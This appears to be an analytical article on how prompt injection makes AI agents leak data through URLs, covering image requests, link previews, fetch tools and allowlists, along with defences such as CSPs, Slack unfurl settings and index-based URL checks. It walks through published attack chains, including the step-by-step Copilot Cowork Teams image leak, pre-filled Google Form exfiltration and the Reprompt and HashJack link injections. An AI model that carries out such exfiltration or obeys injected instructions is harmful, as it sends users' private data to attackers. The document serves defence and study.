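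Protections outside the model can also fail. Moonlock's *AI browsers are clueless about phishing and scams, study finds* reports that Google Safe Browsing is active in Comet but didn't block a page it should have blocked. LayerX, another security vendor, found that Comet's own phishing protection was far weaker than Microsoft Edge's. An agent in such a browser depends on the model's judgement more than its makers may have intended.

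Guardio tested Comet again in 2026 and used the agent's running commentary to refine a scam page until it worked, which took less than four minutes, according to The Hacker News (2026). Like the rewritten templates in MalURLBench, this shows that a single test with fixed material reveals little about what a determined attacker could do.

### Recognising a scam too late

The password manager company 1Password tested eight models with a simulated inbox, browser and password vault. In one of its 30 scenarios, an email links to a shared document at an address with this structure:

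```
https://files.example.com-docs.example/timeline
```

The registrable domain is `com-docs.example`, because a hyphen doesn't separate the parts of a host name. Claude Opus 4.6, the best model in the test, opened the link, fetched the user's password from the vault and submitted it. It then warned the user that the domain was a look-alike and explained why accurately, so it was able to read the address correctly. Meller (2026), in *1Password's new benchmark teaches AI agents how not to get scammed*, reports an average safety score of 13% for this scenario.

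With about 1,200 words of general security guidance in the prompt, every model scored 100% on the disguised-address scenario. One rule in the guidance is to read a link's domain from right to left before opening the link. Over all 30 scenarios, the average score of the weakest model, Gemini 2.5 Flash, rose from 35% to 95%.

That is a large effect for a simple measure, but it comes from a preliminary test by a company that wrote both the scenarios and the guidance. In one place the post reports that critical failures fell from 65 to 2, and in another from 287 to 10, without explaining the difference. Meller also doesn't report how often the guidance made models refuse harmless links, which is the figure developers would most want given Litvak's results with cautious prompts.

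The newest evidence comes from *ScamWorld* (Wu, Liu and colleagues, 2026), which rebuilt 363 reported scam sites in a safe environment and added 53 legitimate ones. It tested agents running on six recent models, including Claude Haiku 5.5 and DeepSeek V4.1 Flash, and used the website's log to check whether an agent had paid, submitted a password or taken some other final step.

Depending on the model, the agents took that step in 11% to 35% of the scam tasks. When the researchers asked the same models whether a site was a scam, they recognised 88% to 100% of the scam sites and wrongly flagged at most 9% of the legitimate ones. DeepSeek V4.1 Flash was deceived in 35% of the scam tasks but recognised 98% of the scam sites. Some agents remarked on suspicious terms during a task but went ahead, treating the user's original request as permission to accept whatever the site required.

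Wu and colleagues started the agent on the scam site, so they didn't test whether it would have chosen the link. They also made sure each site showed a warning sign before the final step, and had to add one to about half the sites. Real scams may have fewer warning signs. A one-sentence warning in the prompt made agents less likely to fall for a scam but also less likely to finish legitimate tasks, as in the email tests.

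The false-alarm rate is still much lower than the 50% to 70% that some models reached when they judged emails. The models in ScamWorld are newer, and they also had much more evidence because they could look around the site before answering. An agent can collect that evidence only by visiting the address, which may be acceptable if the agent holds no passwords, can't pay for anything and sends no private data in the address.

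## When is a link fetched without a click?

An agent's judgement of a link does little good if another program requests the address first. Images in displayed text, link previews in messaging apps, and the agent's own fetching tool are common features that can send a request without a click. OpenAI gives the first two as examples of background requests that a user may never notice.

| Request | Who sends it | From where | First check that could stop it |
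|---|---|---|---|
| Image in an answer | the program that displays the answer | usually the user's device | a filter between the model and the renderer |
| Link preview | the messaging app's preview service | in Slack, the company's servers | the agent's software, before it posts the message |
| Page fetched by a tool | the agent's tool | the provider's servers or the user's computer | a check on the tool call |

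An inspector that isn't where the link is fetched may detect only part of the URL or none of it. A company firewall can detect an employee's browser connecting to `example.net`, though HTTPS normally hides the path and query. If Slack's servers fetch the same address, the firewall detects only ordinary traffic to Slack.

### Images in answers and messages

A filter can remove an image from an answer before the browser requests it, and the page's content security policy can block the request. EchoLeak's image got past both checks. These checks also cover only the page that displays the answer, so they don't apply when an agent sends an image in an email or chat message, which another program will display later under its own rules.

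PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes a leak of this kind in Copilot Cowork, an agent that Microsoft offers through a preview programme. According to PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026), the agent runs in Microsoft's cloud with the user's identity and relies largely on Anthropic's Claude models. Willison (2026) covered the leak on 26 May and called preventing such theft the biggest challenge in designing agents.

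Microsoft's documentation said that Cowork asks for permission before it sends an email or posts a Teams message. PromptArmor found that it didn't ask when the recipient was its own user, and that users couldn't change this. Although nobody else receives such a message, it could contain images from outside websites, and opening it in Teams or Outlook could trigger requests to those sites.

The demonstration used Teams:

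1. The user uploads a skill, a file of reusable instructions for the agent, without knowing that it contains an injection.
2. The user asks for a review of the week's work, and Cowork loads the skill.
3. Cowork obtains download links for the user's recent files. The links are pre-authenticated, so anyone who has one can download the file without logging in.
4. Cowork sends the user a Teams message with images whose addresses contain those links.
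5. The user opens the message, and the image requests deliver the links to the attacker's server.

The length of an address normally limits how much data it can carry. A pre-authenticated link avoids this limit, because a short string gives access to a whole file.

The attack worked in all five trials, though five trials with one injection don't give a reliable success rate. With Cowork's automatic setting, which switched between Claude Opus 4.7 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, it leaked several files. With Opus 4.7, the more capable model, selected, the same injection leaked more because the model searched more thoroughly for recent documents.

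An inspector could have found the image addresses in the tool call that posted the message. A check on Cowork's chat answer would have missed them. The user would have missed them too, because Cowork's record of its actions didn't show the message's content. Asking the user for approval would help only if the approval screen showed the addresses as text. A screen that rendered the message could load the images before the user decided.

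PromptArmor presented the problem as a design risk and reported no fix. It recommends reducing the agent's access to files and, where necessary, blocking downloads from SharePoint. Blocking downloads means users can open the affected files only in a browser and can't print them or use them in Word or Excel, which many offices would find hard to accept. Blocking outside images in messages that the agent sends would disrupt work much less, but only Microsoft can make that change for everyone. The risk is greater for scheduled tasks, since a weekly review can repeat the leak with nobody watching.

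### Link previews in messaging apps

Link previews were mostly harmless when people chose the links, but they leak data when an injection makes an agent put private details in a link's address. Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* explained the problem in 2024, using Slack as an example. Willison (2024), who follows prompt injection closely, wrote that he hadn't thought of this way of leaking data before.

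In February 2026, the security company PromptArmor opened a public test. Users had their own agents write a link to a test website, which recorded any preview request and the data in it. They could then report which agent and messaging app had produced the request, or report a pairing that had produced none. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* singles out OpenClaw, a popular agent that people often use through messaging apps. With its default Telegram configuration, OpenClaw leaked the data as soon as it replied. The remedy is one line in OpenClaw's configuration file:

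```
"channels": {
  "telegram": {
    "linkPreview": false
  }
}
```

With this setting, the test website no longer received any data.

Apostol, in *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, names Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building agents, among the affected systems. SoftwareSeni's *The Agentic Browser Attack Surface You Are Not Thinking About*, a software company's summary of the tests, gives a longer list:

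| Agent | Messaging app | Reported result |
|---|---|---|
| OpenClaw | Telegram | previews on by default |
| OpenClaw | Discord | at risk |
| Cursor, a coding assistant | Slack | at risk |
| Agents built with Copilot Studio | Microsoft Teams | at risk, with the most recorded previews |
| Claude app | Slack | safer |

Teams had the most previews, which SoftwareSeni attributes to the large number of companies that use it. The participants also chose which systems to test, so the count doesn't measure risk per message. The two Slack entries, one on each side of the list, are more informative. The split makes sense because Slack lets the software that posts a message turn off its preview.

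PromptArmor has closed the test and published the final results. Its updated post reports no change to OpenClaw's default and still recommends the manual setting. Microsoft's fix for EchoLeak closed one leak through a Teams service but didn't remove previews from Teams in general. The test results describe early 2026, so anyone who runs one of these pairings should repeat the test with their own server and made-up data.

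PromptArmor wants messaging apps to offer preview settings for individual chats and channels. An administrator could then protect a channel used by several agents without relying on each agent's developer.

### Switching previews off in Slack

Slack calls previews "unfurls". An app can disable them for a message with two fields described in Slack's *chat.postMessage method*:

```
{
  "channel": "C123456",
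  "text": "The invoice is at https://example.com/march",
  "unfurl_links": false,
  "unfurl_media": false
}
```

`unfurl_links` controls previews of pages that consist mainly of text, and `unfurl_media` controls previews of images, video and audio. The app needs to disable both. According to Slack's *Unfurling links in messages*, Slack's servers have to fetch an address to determine which kind of content it has. If an app disables only one kind of preview, Slack may still request the address to find out whether the setting applies, and that request would send out any data the address contains.

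Developers shouldn't rely on the defaults either. Slack states that it unfurls all links that apps post, but its examples include a text page that unfurls only when the app requests it. The fields apply to one message at a time, so every part of the program that posts to Slack has to set them. It is safest to set them in a single function that sends all outgoing messages.

Some of Slack's other rules suppress previews without offering the same protection. A link doesn't unfurl if its visible text is just the address without `https://`, and Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences* adds that links don't expand in a message with more than five of them. An injection can get around both rules by telling the agent to write one link with different text. Members can hide previews in their own preferences, but other people may read the same message. Slack's *Manage link previews* explains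 how to block previews from a particular website, but this doesn't help against a domain that an attacker has just registered.

A link preview in Slack can leak a person's data even if they aren't using Slack to talk to the agent. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* describes a developer who asks Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to analyse a source file containing invisible instructions. The agent reads a secret key from a local file and posts it to Slack inside a link, using Anthropic's Slack server for the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting models to tools. Slack's preview service then fetches the link, which sends the key to the attacker's server. If the link points to an image, the server receives several requests, with the user agents Slack-LinkExpanding, Slackbot and Slack-ImgProxy.

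This flaw is CVE-2025-34072. Snyk's *Improper Neutralization of Input Used for LLM Prompting* (2025) lists no fixed version of the package, so a team that still uses it would have to add the two settings itself or replace the package. In its guide, Slack now advises developers to consider disabling unfurls for messages from a language model.

### The agent's own fetching tool

When an agent fetches a page itself, its software has the complete address before any request leaves, so a check at this point is better placed than a firewall or a filter on the answer. The check has to cover every request the tool makes, including redirects and links it follows from a fetched page. The attack on Claude's page-fetching tool that Willison (2026) covered also used cloaking, in which the server showed a hostile page only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude.

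Like Slack's previews, the link previews that some assistants fetch for the model send data out, but they also bring in text written by an outsider. Lan and colleagues call the result implicit prompt injection because the instructions enter through an automatic step that the user neither requested nor saw.

In their test, they placed the instructions in the page's title, its metadata description, its body or the text of a link. The agent reached each page either directly or through redirects, and the instructions told it to send the data either whole or in four pieces. With 30 runs for each combination, this gives

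$$4 \times 2 \times 2 \times 30 = 480 \text{ runs}.$$

The attacker's server received a request in 423 of these runs and in none of 120 further runs with harmless pages, so the injected instructions caused the leaks, not random requests by a small model. When the agent sent the data whole, the position of the instructions made little difference. The attack succeeded in 96.7% of runs with the instructions in the metadata description and in every run with them in the other three positions.

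The experiment doesn't quite match the definition, because the user always asked for a summary of the page and so requested its content, though not its hidden metadata. A test in which the user only mentioned an address would have isolated the automatic step better.

### What splitting the data changed

Lan and colleagues measured leakage through the first $k$ requests of a run with a quantity they call Leak@$k$:

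$$\text{Leak@}k = \frac{\text{runs with sensitive data in the first } k \text{ requests}}{\text{all runs}}.$$

These are the averages over all positions and both ways of reaching the page:

| Measure | Data sent whole | Data split in four |
|---|---|---|
| Attacker received any request | 99.2% | 77.1% |
| Leak@1 | 96.7% | 26.3% |
| Leak@3 | 96.7% | 15.8% |

The 73% reduction is the fall in Leak@1 from 96.7% to 26.3%. Part of the drop came from failed attacks, because the small model often couldn't carry out the longer instructions. Among runs that sent something, Leak@1 fell from about 97% to 34%, a reduction of roughly 65%.

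The reported Leak@3 is lower than Leak@1, which should be impossible under the published definition because the first three requests include the first one. The definition also counts any fragment of the secret as a leak, so a first request carrying a quarter of the secret should count. The software that scored the runs probably missed many short fragments. That would support the point that a filter can miss them too, but it makes the 73% a rough indication at best. The paper also defines a rate for runs in which all the pieces arrived but gives no value for it, so it is unclear how often the attacker could have reassembled the secret.

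### Warnings in the prompt against checks on the request

In a separate experiment, the team tested defences against instructions in the page's body that sent the data whole. Each condition had 30 runs.

| Defence | Runs with an attempt | Runs with a leak |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| Warning in the system prompt | 20 | 20 |
| Tags around outside text | 30 | 30 |
| Warning and tags | 17 | 17 |
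| List of permitted domains | 30 | 0 |
| Rules for suspicious addresses | 25 | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 7 | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0 | 0 |
| All of them | 0 | 0 |

The tags alone had no effect, even though the prompt described their contents as untrusted data. The warning stopped a third of the attacks. Adding the tags to the warning prevented three more leaks, which could easily be chance with so few runs.

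The domain list shows the advantage of checking the request. The injection succeeded in every run, since the agent always tried to send the data, but the tool refused each time. Because the attacker's domain wasn't on the list, any correctly written check would have blocked every attempt. The experiment doesn't show how well such a list works when an attacker can use a service on a permitted domain.

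The rules for suspicious addresses block numeric addresses, certain domain endings and paths containing words such as "collect". Lan and colleagues call this "redirect detection", but the rules don't examine redirects. The paper's example attack has "collect" in its path, and an attacker could choose another word.

The results for the two content filters are harder to interpret. Both filters check a request after the model has written it, so they shouldn't affect how often the model tries to send one. Yet attempts fell from 30 to 7 with one filter and to none with the other. The paper suggests that the model avoided random-looking values while the filter was active, but doesn't explain how information about the filter could have reached the model. The filter for random-looking values never blocked anything in the experiment, so the absence of leaks isn't evidence that it works.

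Its rule also has a clear weakness. It blocks values of more than 10 characters whose Shannon entropy, a measure of how varied the characters are, exceeds 4 bits:

$$H = -\sum_c p_c \log_2 p_c,$$

where $p_c$ is the share of the value made up of character $c$. The 20-character key that the paper uses as an example has an entropy of about 3.85 bits, so it would pass whole. A four-character piece is too short for the rule and can't exceed $\log_2 4 = 2$ bits anyway. The team didn't run the filters against split data, but this arithmetic supports its claim that splitting defeats them. A domain list, by contrast, refuses each piece for the same reason as the whole.

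All these tests favoured the attacker, because the secret was in plain view and the tool was explicitly described. Lan and colleagues suggest that models more capable than qwen2.5:7b might be easier to exploit because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. They didn't test this, and training against injections could make them harder to exploit. A much stronger model failed every time in Copilot Cowork, though with a different injection and product.

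The testbed also recorded only web requests, not name lookups. A fetcher normally has to look up `leeds.example.net` before contacting it, and that lookup can reach a name server run by the holder of `example.net`. A tool that looks up the host before checking its list of permitted domains can therefore leak the city even when it refuses the request.

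## Why is a trusted domain not enough?

A list of permitted domains stopped every leak in Lan and colleagues' test because the attacker's server wasn't on it. Researchers got around similar lists in several commercial products by sending the data to a permitted domain. Others used links to genuine Microsoft and Atlassian sites to deliver instructions to the agent.

These attacks are possible because a domain's owner decides how its servers respond, but whoever writes a link chooses the path, query and fragment. Trusting the domain therefore doesn't justify trusting the rest of the address.

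### What allowlists and content security policies check

An allowlist names the domains or addresses that a program may contact, and the program refuses everything else. An agent's maker can enforce one in the page-fetching tool or in the network settings of the machine where the agent runs code. For a web page, the maker can use a CSP, which the browser enforces. This one covers images:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://images.example.com https://*.example.net
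```

It permits images from the page's own site, from `images.example.com`, and from every subdomain of `example.net`, including any its owner adds later. For each image, the browser compares the scheme, host and port with the entries. It ignores the query, so `https://images.example.com/chart.png?city=Leeds` passes. An entry can also name a path, such as `https://images.example.com/charts/`, but the browser ignores the path when it checks where a redirect leads.

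A CSP doesn't restrict ordinary clicks on links to other sites. Neither kind of list can show who reads a request at its destination, whether the server forwards it, or whether the domain still belongs to the company the list's author had in mind.

### Domains that keep what they receive

Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, had a CSP that blocked images from unknown domains but allowed `docs.google.com`. Google Forms runs on that domain, where anyone can create a form and read the responses. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an email whose hidden instructions exploited this. When the user asked for a summary of recent mail, the assistant wrote an image with other emails' contents in its address. With a reserved domain, the address had this structure:

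```
https://docs.example.com/forms/123/response?entry=Leeds
```

Google Forms supports links with the answers already filled in, and requesting one submits the form. When the browser tried to load the image, Google stored the data as a response that the form's owner could read, even though no image came back.

The user never had to open the hostile email. PromptArmor extracted the full text of several emails in one answer and parts of more than 40 in another. Willison (2026), in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, traces the leak to the CSP rule, because Google Forms saves data sent in a GET request. Browsers load images with GET requests, which under web standards should only retrieve data. Someone reviewing the domain with documents in mind could easily have missed a form that breaks this convention.

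PromptArmor reported the flaw on Friday, 5 December 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday, deployed its first patch on Tuesday, and released the last patches on 11 January 2026, a day before publication. PromptArmor praises the response but doesn't explain what the patches changed.

The same route worked a few months later in Codex, a coding agent that OpenAI had extended to everyday office tasks. According to PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* (2026), a hostile email made Codex submit other emails to a Google Form through an image. OpenAI has fixed this. The post doesn't mention an allowlist, so the attacker may not have needed Google's domain. A form is still convenient because it saves the attacker from running a server.

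Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine that blocks nearly all outside domains but allows Anthropic's own API, the interface through which other programs use the company's models and store files. Two days after Cowork's release in January 2026, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* described how hidden instructions in a document could make the agent upload a user's file to that API without asking for approval. The instructions included the attacker's API key, a code that identifies an account, so the file went to the attacker's account. The demonstration used a Claude Haiku model, but Claude Opus 4.5, which is harder to manipulate, leaked customer records the same way in another test.

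The address in this attack contains no private data and is the same one a legitimate upload uses. The file travels in the body of the request, and only the key determines which account receives it. An inspector that checks only addresses can't distinguish the two uploads, however well it parses the addresses. One fix would be to send all such requests through a gateway that inserts the user's own key and discards any other.

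Johann Rehberger had reported the underlying flaw in Claude's chat product before Cowork existed. Anthropic had acknowledged the flaw but not fixed it when PromptArmor published its findings. According to TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection*, Anthropic was updating the virtual machine to restrict file access. That limits what an attacker can steal, but doesn't by itself stop uploads to another account.

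Google's mistake with Antigravity, a code editor with built-in agents, was more obvious. The default allowlist for the agent's browser included webhook.site, a service that gives anyone an address and shows them every request sent to it. Developers use such services for testing, which may be why it was on the list. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, from November 2025, describes an online programming guide with instructions in tiny type that made the agent collect credentials and code, put them in a webhook.site address and open that address.

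Antigravity had a rule against reading the credentials file. The rule covered only the agent's file-reading tool, so the agent printed the file with a terminal command instead.

PromptArmor didn't report the leak to Google, because Antigravity already warned new users about this risk. Willison writes that Google's page for security researchers listed leaks through the browser agent as a known issue that the company was working to fix. Neither post reports a completed fix. Anyone who still has that default list should remove webhook.site, though PromptArmor also found three ways to leak data without the browser.

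### When a domain changes hands

Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for business agents, had a CSP that permitted images from subdomains of `my-salesforce-cms.com`, a domain whose registration had expired. The security company Noma registered the domain, for $5 according to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, and could then receive whatever Agentforce sent there.

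The attack, which Noma called ForcedLeak, began with a form on a company's public website. Salesforce can turn each submission into a sales lead, and an attacker could put instructions in a field. When an employee later asked Agentforce about that lead, the agent put the email addresses of the company's leads into an image URL.

Noma called the discovery of the expired domain essential. Salesforce Ben, a news site about Salesforce products, quotes the company as saying that the theft "would have been impossible" without a way around the CSP. The policy otherwise worked, but one forgotten entry made it possible to bypass.

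Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce patched it by 8 September, according to Information Security Buzz. Salesforce regained control of the domain and corrected the CSP. It also introduced Trusted URLs, which prevents Agentforce and Einstein AI agents from sending output to untrusted addresses (The Hacker News, 2025).

Trusted URLs applies to what the agent writes, so it can also stop a link that needs a click, which a CSP can't. But it is still an allowlist, and it would have approved the expired domain if that domain had been listed. A company can renew its own domains or delete them from its lists before they expire. It doesn't have that control over its suppliers' domains, so it has to recheck those entries regularly.

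Wildcard entries have a related weakness, because an outsider can gain control of a subdomain while the company still owns the domain. If `old.example.com` still points to a cloud service that the company has stopped using, an outsider may be able to claim the company's old space there and receive requests sent to the subdomain.

### Genuine links that carry instructions

Many AI assistants accept a prompt in a link. For example, `https://assistant.example/?q=What+is+Markdown` opens the assistant with the question already entered. This is useful for bookmarks and search boxes, but it also lets a stranger write a prompt for someone else's assistant. SearchLeak used this feature in Copilot Enterprise Search, and Varonis found the same weakness in three other attacks.

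Varonis' *Reprompt* (2026) describes an attack on Microsoft's consumer version of Copilot. The victim clicked a genuine Microsoft link, and Copilot followed the instructions in the link's query string. Copilot removed sensitive data from the addresses it fetched, but only on the first request, so a repeated request got the data through. The attacker's server then answered each request with new instructions, which could depend on what Copilot had just revealed. Someone who read the entire original link therefore couldn't have worked out what data the attacker would steal.

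Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes a later attack on the same product. The attack could reach Gmail, Google Drive and other services the user had connected, and in one test Copilot retrieved an email with a password in plain text. According to *CoSnitch*, the `q` parameter only fills in the input box, and a second, undocumented parameter made the prompt run. Varonis' researchers discovered the second parameter by repeatedly asking Copilot why prompts couldn't run automatically. The Reprompt post, however, describes prompts that ran as soon as the page loaded. Microsoft may have changed this between the tests, but Varonis doesn't explain the difference.

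Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) applies the method to Rovo, the AI assistant of Atlassian, which makes the task tracker Jira and the document system Confluence. If a link left out the organisation's identifier, Atlassian opened the victim's default organisation, so an attacker could send the same link to employees of many companies. Rovo did not warn users that the prompt had come from a link, and its built-in research agent could browse any website, which gave the attacker a way to send the data out.

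HashJack, which Cato Networks (2025) disclosed, puts instructions after the number sign in a link to any legitimate website, not just an assistant's site. Some AI browsers passed this fragment to their assistant along with the rest of the address, and the assistant followed the instructions. F5's *HashJack Attack Targets AI Browsers and Agentic AI Systems* points out that web application firewalls and server logs miss the attack because the fragment never reaches them.

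| Attack | Product | Location of the instructions | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reprompt | Copilot Personal | query | Microsoft patched it by January 2026 |
| CoSnitch | Copilot Personal | query | Microsoft patched it in August 2026, eight months after the report |
| RovoBlast | Rovo | query | Atlassian changed its servers on 8 July 2026 |
| HashJack | Comet, Copilot for Edge, Gemini for Chrome | fragment | Perplexity and Microsoft fixed their products, but Gemini was still vulnerable in November 2025 |

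The Hacker News (2026) gives the date for RovoBlast, and Hackread's *HashJack Attack Uses URL ‘#’ to Control AI Browser Behavior* (2025) gives the status of the HashJack fixes. HashJack didn't work on Claude for Chrome or OpenAI's Atlas, according to Help Net Security's *New “HashJack” attack can hijack AI browsers and assistants*, so the flaw isn't inherent in AI browsers.

All these links pass a reputation check, which looks up whether a domain has a record of phishing or malware, and perhaps how old it is. Microsoft's and Atlassian's domains are old and genuine. Visiting the page in advance doesn't help much either, because the harm depends on the victim's session and connected accounts. A scanner without the victim's login would probably get an ordinary start page. An organisation could block the domain, but then nobody there could use the assistant.

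An inspector can still check links to known assistants for text in the query, and show that text to the user or remove it. This requires a list of each assistant's parameters, which would not have included the undocumented parameter in CoSnitch. The assistant's maker is better placed to solve the problem. It can put the text in the input box, label it as coming from a link and wait for the user to send it. Some users will press Enter without reading, so the safeguards against leaks also have to cover the whole session. Varonis recommends in its Reprompt post that these safeguards persist through repeated and follow-up requests.

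In a statement in SecurityWeek's *Critical One-Click Vulnerability in Atlassian’s Rovo AI Exposed Enterprise Data*, Atlassian advises customers to verify that any content they give its apps comes from a trusted source. This advice is reasonable for uploaded files but less convincing for links, because an employee who checked a RovoBlast link would have found Atlassian's own domain.

To defend against HashJack, a browser can remove the fragment from the address it gives the model and keep the original for displaying the page. An attacker could then try putting the instructions in the query, because many websites ignore parameters they don't recognise. The assistant therefore has to treat the entire address as untrusted text, even if the user clicked on the link.

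### A Rovo leak without a trusted domain

PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls*, published two days before the RovoBlast post, describes a separate flaw that none of these causes explains. The hidden instructions were in a file the user uploaded, and Rovo sent Jira tickets and Confluence pages to the attacker's server without using a trusted domain. Rovo's tool for opening web pages accepted any address, including one the agent had just built from private data.

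The attack still worked when administrators turned off web search for the whole organisation. According to PromptArmor, the setting removed the search but left the tool that opens the results. As with Antigravity's protected file, the restriction blocked one tool but not another that could be used instead.

PromptArmor reported the flaw on 23 May 2026 and said that Rovo was still vulnerable on 5 August. The Hacker News found no confirmation of a fix as of 8 August and noted that nobody had independently reproduced the finding about web search. Customers can restrict which apps and groups use Rovo. But if a site has several Jira apps, Rovo's chat and search stay available until Rovo is disabled in all of them.

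An allowlist on the page-opening tool would have blocked the attack as PromptArmor demonstrated it. The same is true of two other attacks PromptArmor found at Superhuman, in which the mail assistant's web search and a newer product, Superhuman Go, also sent data directly to an attacker's domain.

### What makes a domain safe for automatic requests

An attacker's instructions that control everything in a request except the host can still make the agent send private data to a listed domain. To obtain the data, the attacker must read it there or get the domain to send it elsewhere. A domain is therefore safe for automatic requests only if no outsider can read what the agent sends to it and it forwards nothing.

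In symbols, let $P$ be the people who may have the data, $R(d)$ everyone who can learn something from a request to domain $d$, and $S(d)$ the outside servers to which $d$ passes any part of the request. Then

$$\text{safe}(d) \iff R(d) \subseteq P \ \text{ and } \ S(d) = \varnothing.$$

Google's form service, Anthropic's API and webhook.site all fail the condition on $R$, because an outsider can open an account or create an address there. Salesforce's domain failed it once anybody could register the name. The Teams proxy in EchoLeak and Bing's image search in SearchLeak fail the condition on $S$. PromptArmor seems to have this second risk in mind when it advises Notion, a workspace app, to adopt a strong CSP and make sure its own image server can't redirect requests around the policy.

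$R(d)$ includes people who can't read the data directly but can infer it. If `https://example.com/cities/leeds` shows a public visit count, an attacker without access to any log can create or find one such page per city and watch which count rises.

The condition has to hold for every address that the entry permits. Most pages on `docs.google.com` don't store anything from a request, but the form pages do, so the whole domain fails. An entry limited to a harmless path may pass if the program also enforces that limit after redirects. Analytics services, which many websites include in their CSPs, are a poor choice for a page that shows a model's output. They usually record each request under the customer account number it contains, and the attacker can be a customer too. A host that serves only the company's own fixed files, such as logos and fonts, is a much better choice if outsiders can't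 read its logs.

This condition covers only outgoing data. A domain can meet it and still deliver hostile instructions, for example if strangers can post comments there that the agent later reads.

### The case for a short list

Allowlists are still worth having. Comparing a host with a list takes almost no time and doesn't need a language model. The same address also gets the same result every time, however persuasive the attacker's surrounding text is. A classifier or a warning in the prompt can't guarantee this. Willison objects to probabilistic defences because "99% is a failing grade" in security, where an attacker can keep trying until something gets through.

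The documented failures are also some evidence that lists of trusted domains help. To get data out of Superhuman's mail program through an image, PromptArmor had to find a permitted service that would store the data, whereas in Superhuman Go it used its own domain.

Varonis argues in its RovoBlast post that blocking one exit doesn't eliminate the risk, because attackers look for the next trusted route. This is a strong objection to closing exits one at a time. It is weaker against a list of three trusted routes, because attackers can try only those three and the defender can examine each one properly.

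The length of the list matters a great deal. Suppose, purely for illustration, that each entry has a 2% chance of containing a service that an attacker could use, independently of the others. The chance that a list of $n$ entries has at least one is

$$1 - (1 - 0.02)^n,$$

which is about 6% for 3 entries and 44% for 29, the number in Copilot's image policy at the time of EchoLeak. The real probability for each entry is unknown, and a wildcard can admit hundreds of hosts, so it should count for much more than one.

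Anthropic lets developers limit Claude's page-fetching tool to domains they choose. Willison thinks it should be possible to build safe products this way if none of the domains can leak data, although he calls finding such domains tricky. This is easiest when an assistant displays images only from its maker's own server. But an agent that compares hotels or follows the news has to open pages on domains that nobody could have listed in advance.

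## Is it safe to fetch only addresses that are already known?

An agent that compares hotels can't work from a short list of allowed domains, but its software can apply a stricter rule to each address. Before the agent opens `https://example.net/p?city=Leeds`, the software checks whether that exact address existed before the agent learned that its user lives in Leeds. If it did, the agent can't have built the address from the user's data.

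This rule can allow an unknown hobbyist's page and block an address on a famous domain. It would have blocked the pre-filled Google Form in the Superhuman attack, because the form's address contained the stolen emails and nobody had published it before. It wouldn't have stopped the upload from Claude Cowork, because the address used for the upload contained no private data.

The software needs a record of which addresses are old enough to fetch. OpenAI uses an index of the public web, while Anthropic uses the conversation, which an attacker can add text to much more easily.

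### OpenAI's index of public addresses

When Rehberger reported the leak through image addresses in early 2023, OpenAI had no bug bounty programme, and his emails had little effect. Microsoft fixed the same flaw in Bing Chat that May with a content security policy that generally blocked images. OpenAI added its first check, `url_safe`, in December, but outsiders couldn't tell what made an address safe. Rehberger worked out some of its rules by experiment and presented ways around it at Black Hat Europe in 2024. Further changes around August 2025 stopped those attacks, as he recounts in Embrace The Red.

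In January 2026, OpenAI explained the rule in a blog post and a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. A crawler builds an index of public addresses, as a search engine does, without access to anyone's conversations, account or personal data. When an agent is about to load a page or an image automatically, the software looks for the address in this index. If the address is there, the agent can load it without asking. Otherwise, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation.

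The crawler must find addresses independently of users' chats. Otherwise, an address made from private data could enter the index after the agent's first attempt to fetch it and pass the check on the second.

OpenAI claims only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data. There are exceptions because people sometimes post private links, such as a document's secret sharing link, in public.

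The rule works best for web research, where most useful pages are public, but it suits a mail assistant less well. A supplier may put each invoice at an address with a long random code, and no crawler will have seen that address before the customer does. Password reset and parcel tracking links work the same way. An assistant that handles many such links would have to show many warnings. OpenAI objects to strict allowlists partly because frequent warnings teach people to click through them, and the same objection applies here.

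As Rehberger understands it, ChatGPT also treats an address as safe for the rest of a chat if the user entered it in a message. This exception avoids some needless warnings, but a user who pastes in a whole suspicious email to ask about it may also approve every link in it.

### What counts as a match

A developer who copies the index rule has to decide which differences between two addresses to ignore. Ignoring the query would produce fewer warnings, since many links differ only in their tracking parameters, but it would also let through data in the query, such as `?city=Leeds`. The comparison has to include everything the server receives, but it can leave out the fragment, which the browser doesn't send.

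Even harmless-looking canonicalisation can reopen the leak. These two addresses differ only in how they write the letter m:

```
https://example.net/march
https://example.net/%6Darch
```

If the inspector decodes both spellings of a URL before looking them up, they match the same entry. But a browser sends the path as written, so the server's log records which spelling the agent chose. Each letter that the agent can write in two ways gives the attacker one more bit of information. The fetcher should therefore request the URL as stored in the index, not as the model wrote it.

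Exact matching handles open redirects better than a domain list does. In `https://example.com/go?to=https://example.net/Leeds`, the private data (`Leeds`) is already in the first address, so the lookup fails before the fetcher contacts any server. If a known address redirects, the server chooses the next address using only what it learned from the request. This protection is weaker if the request includes the user's login cookies, because the server could then put the user's account details in the next address. A fetcher that sends no cookies and looks up each address in the redirect chain avoids this problem.

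### Anthropic's rule for its fetch tool

Anthropic offers developers a page-fetching tool for Claude that doesn't need an index of the web. The tool refuses any address that hasn't already appeared in the conversation. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* lists three permitted sources:

- messages from the user
- results from the developer's own tools
- results from earlier web searches and fetches

An address that appears only in Claude's own output doesn't count as known, so an injected instruction to attach a secret to an attacker's address and open the result will fail even if it convinces Claude. Willison (2025) had hoped for a narrower rule that accepted only addresses from the user's prompts.

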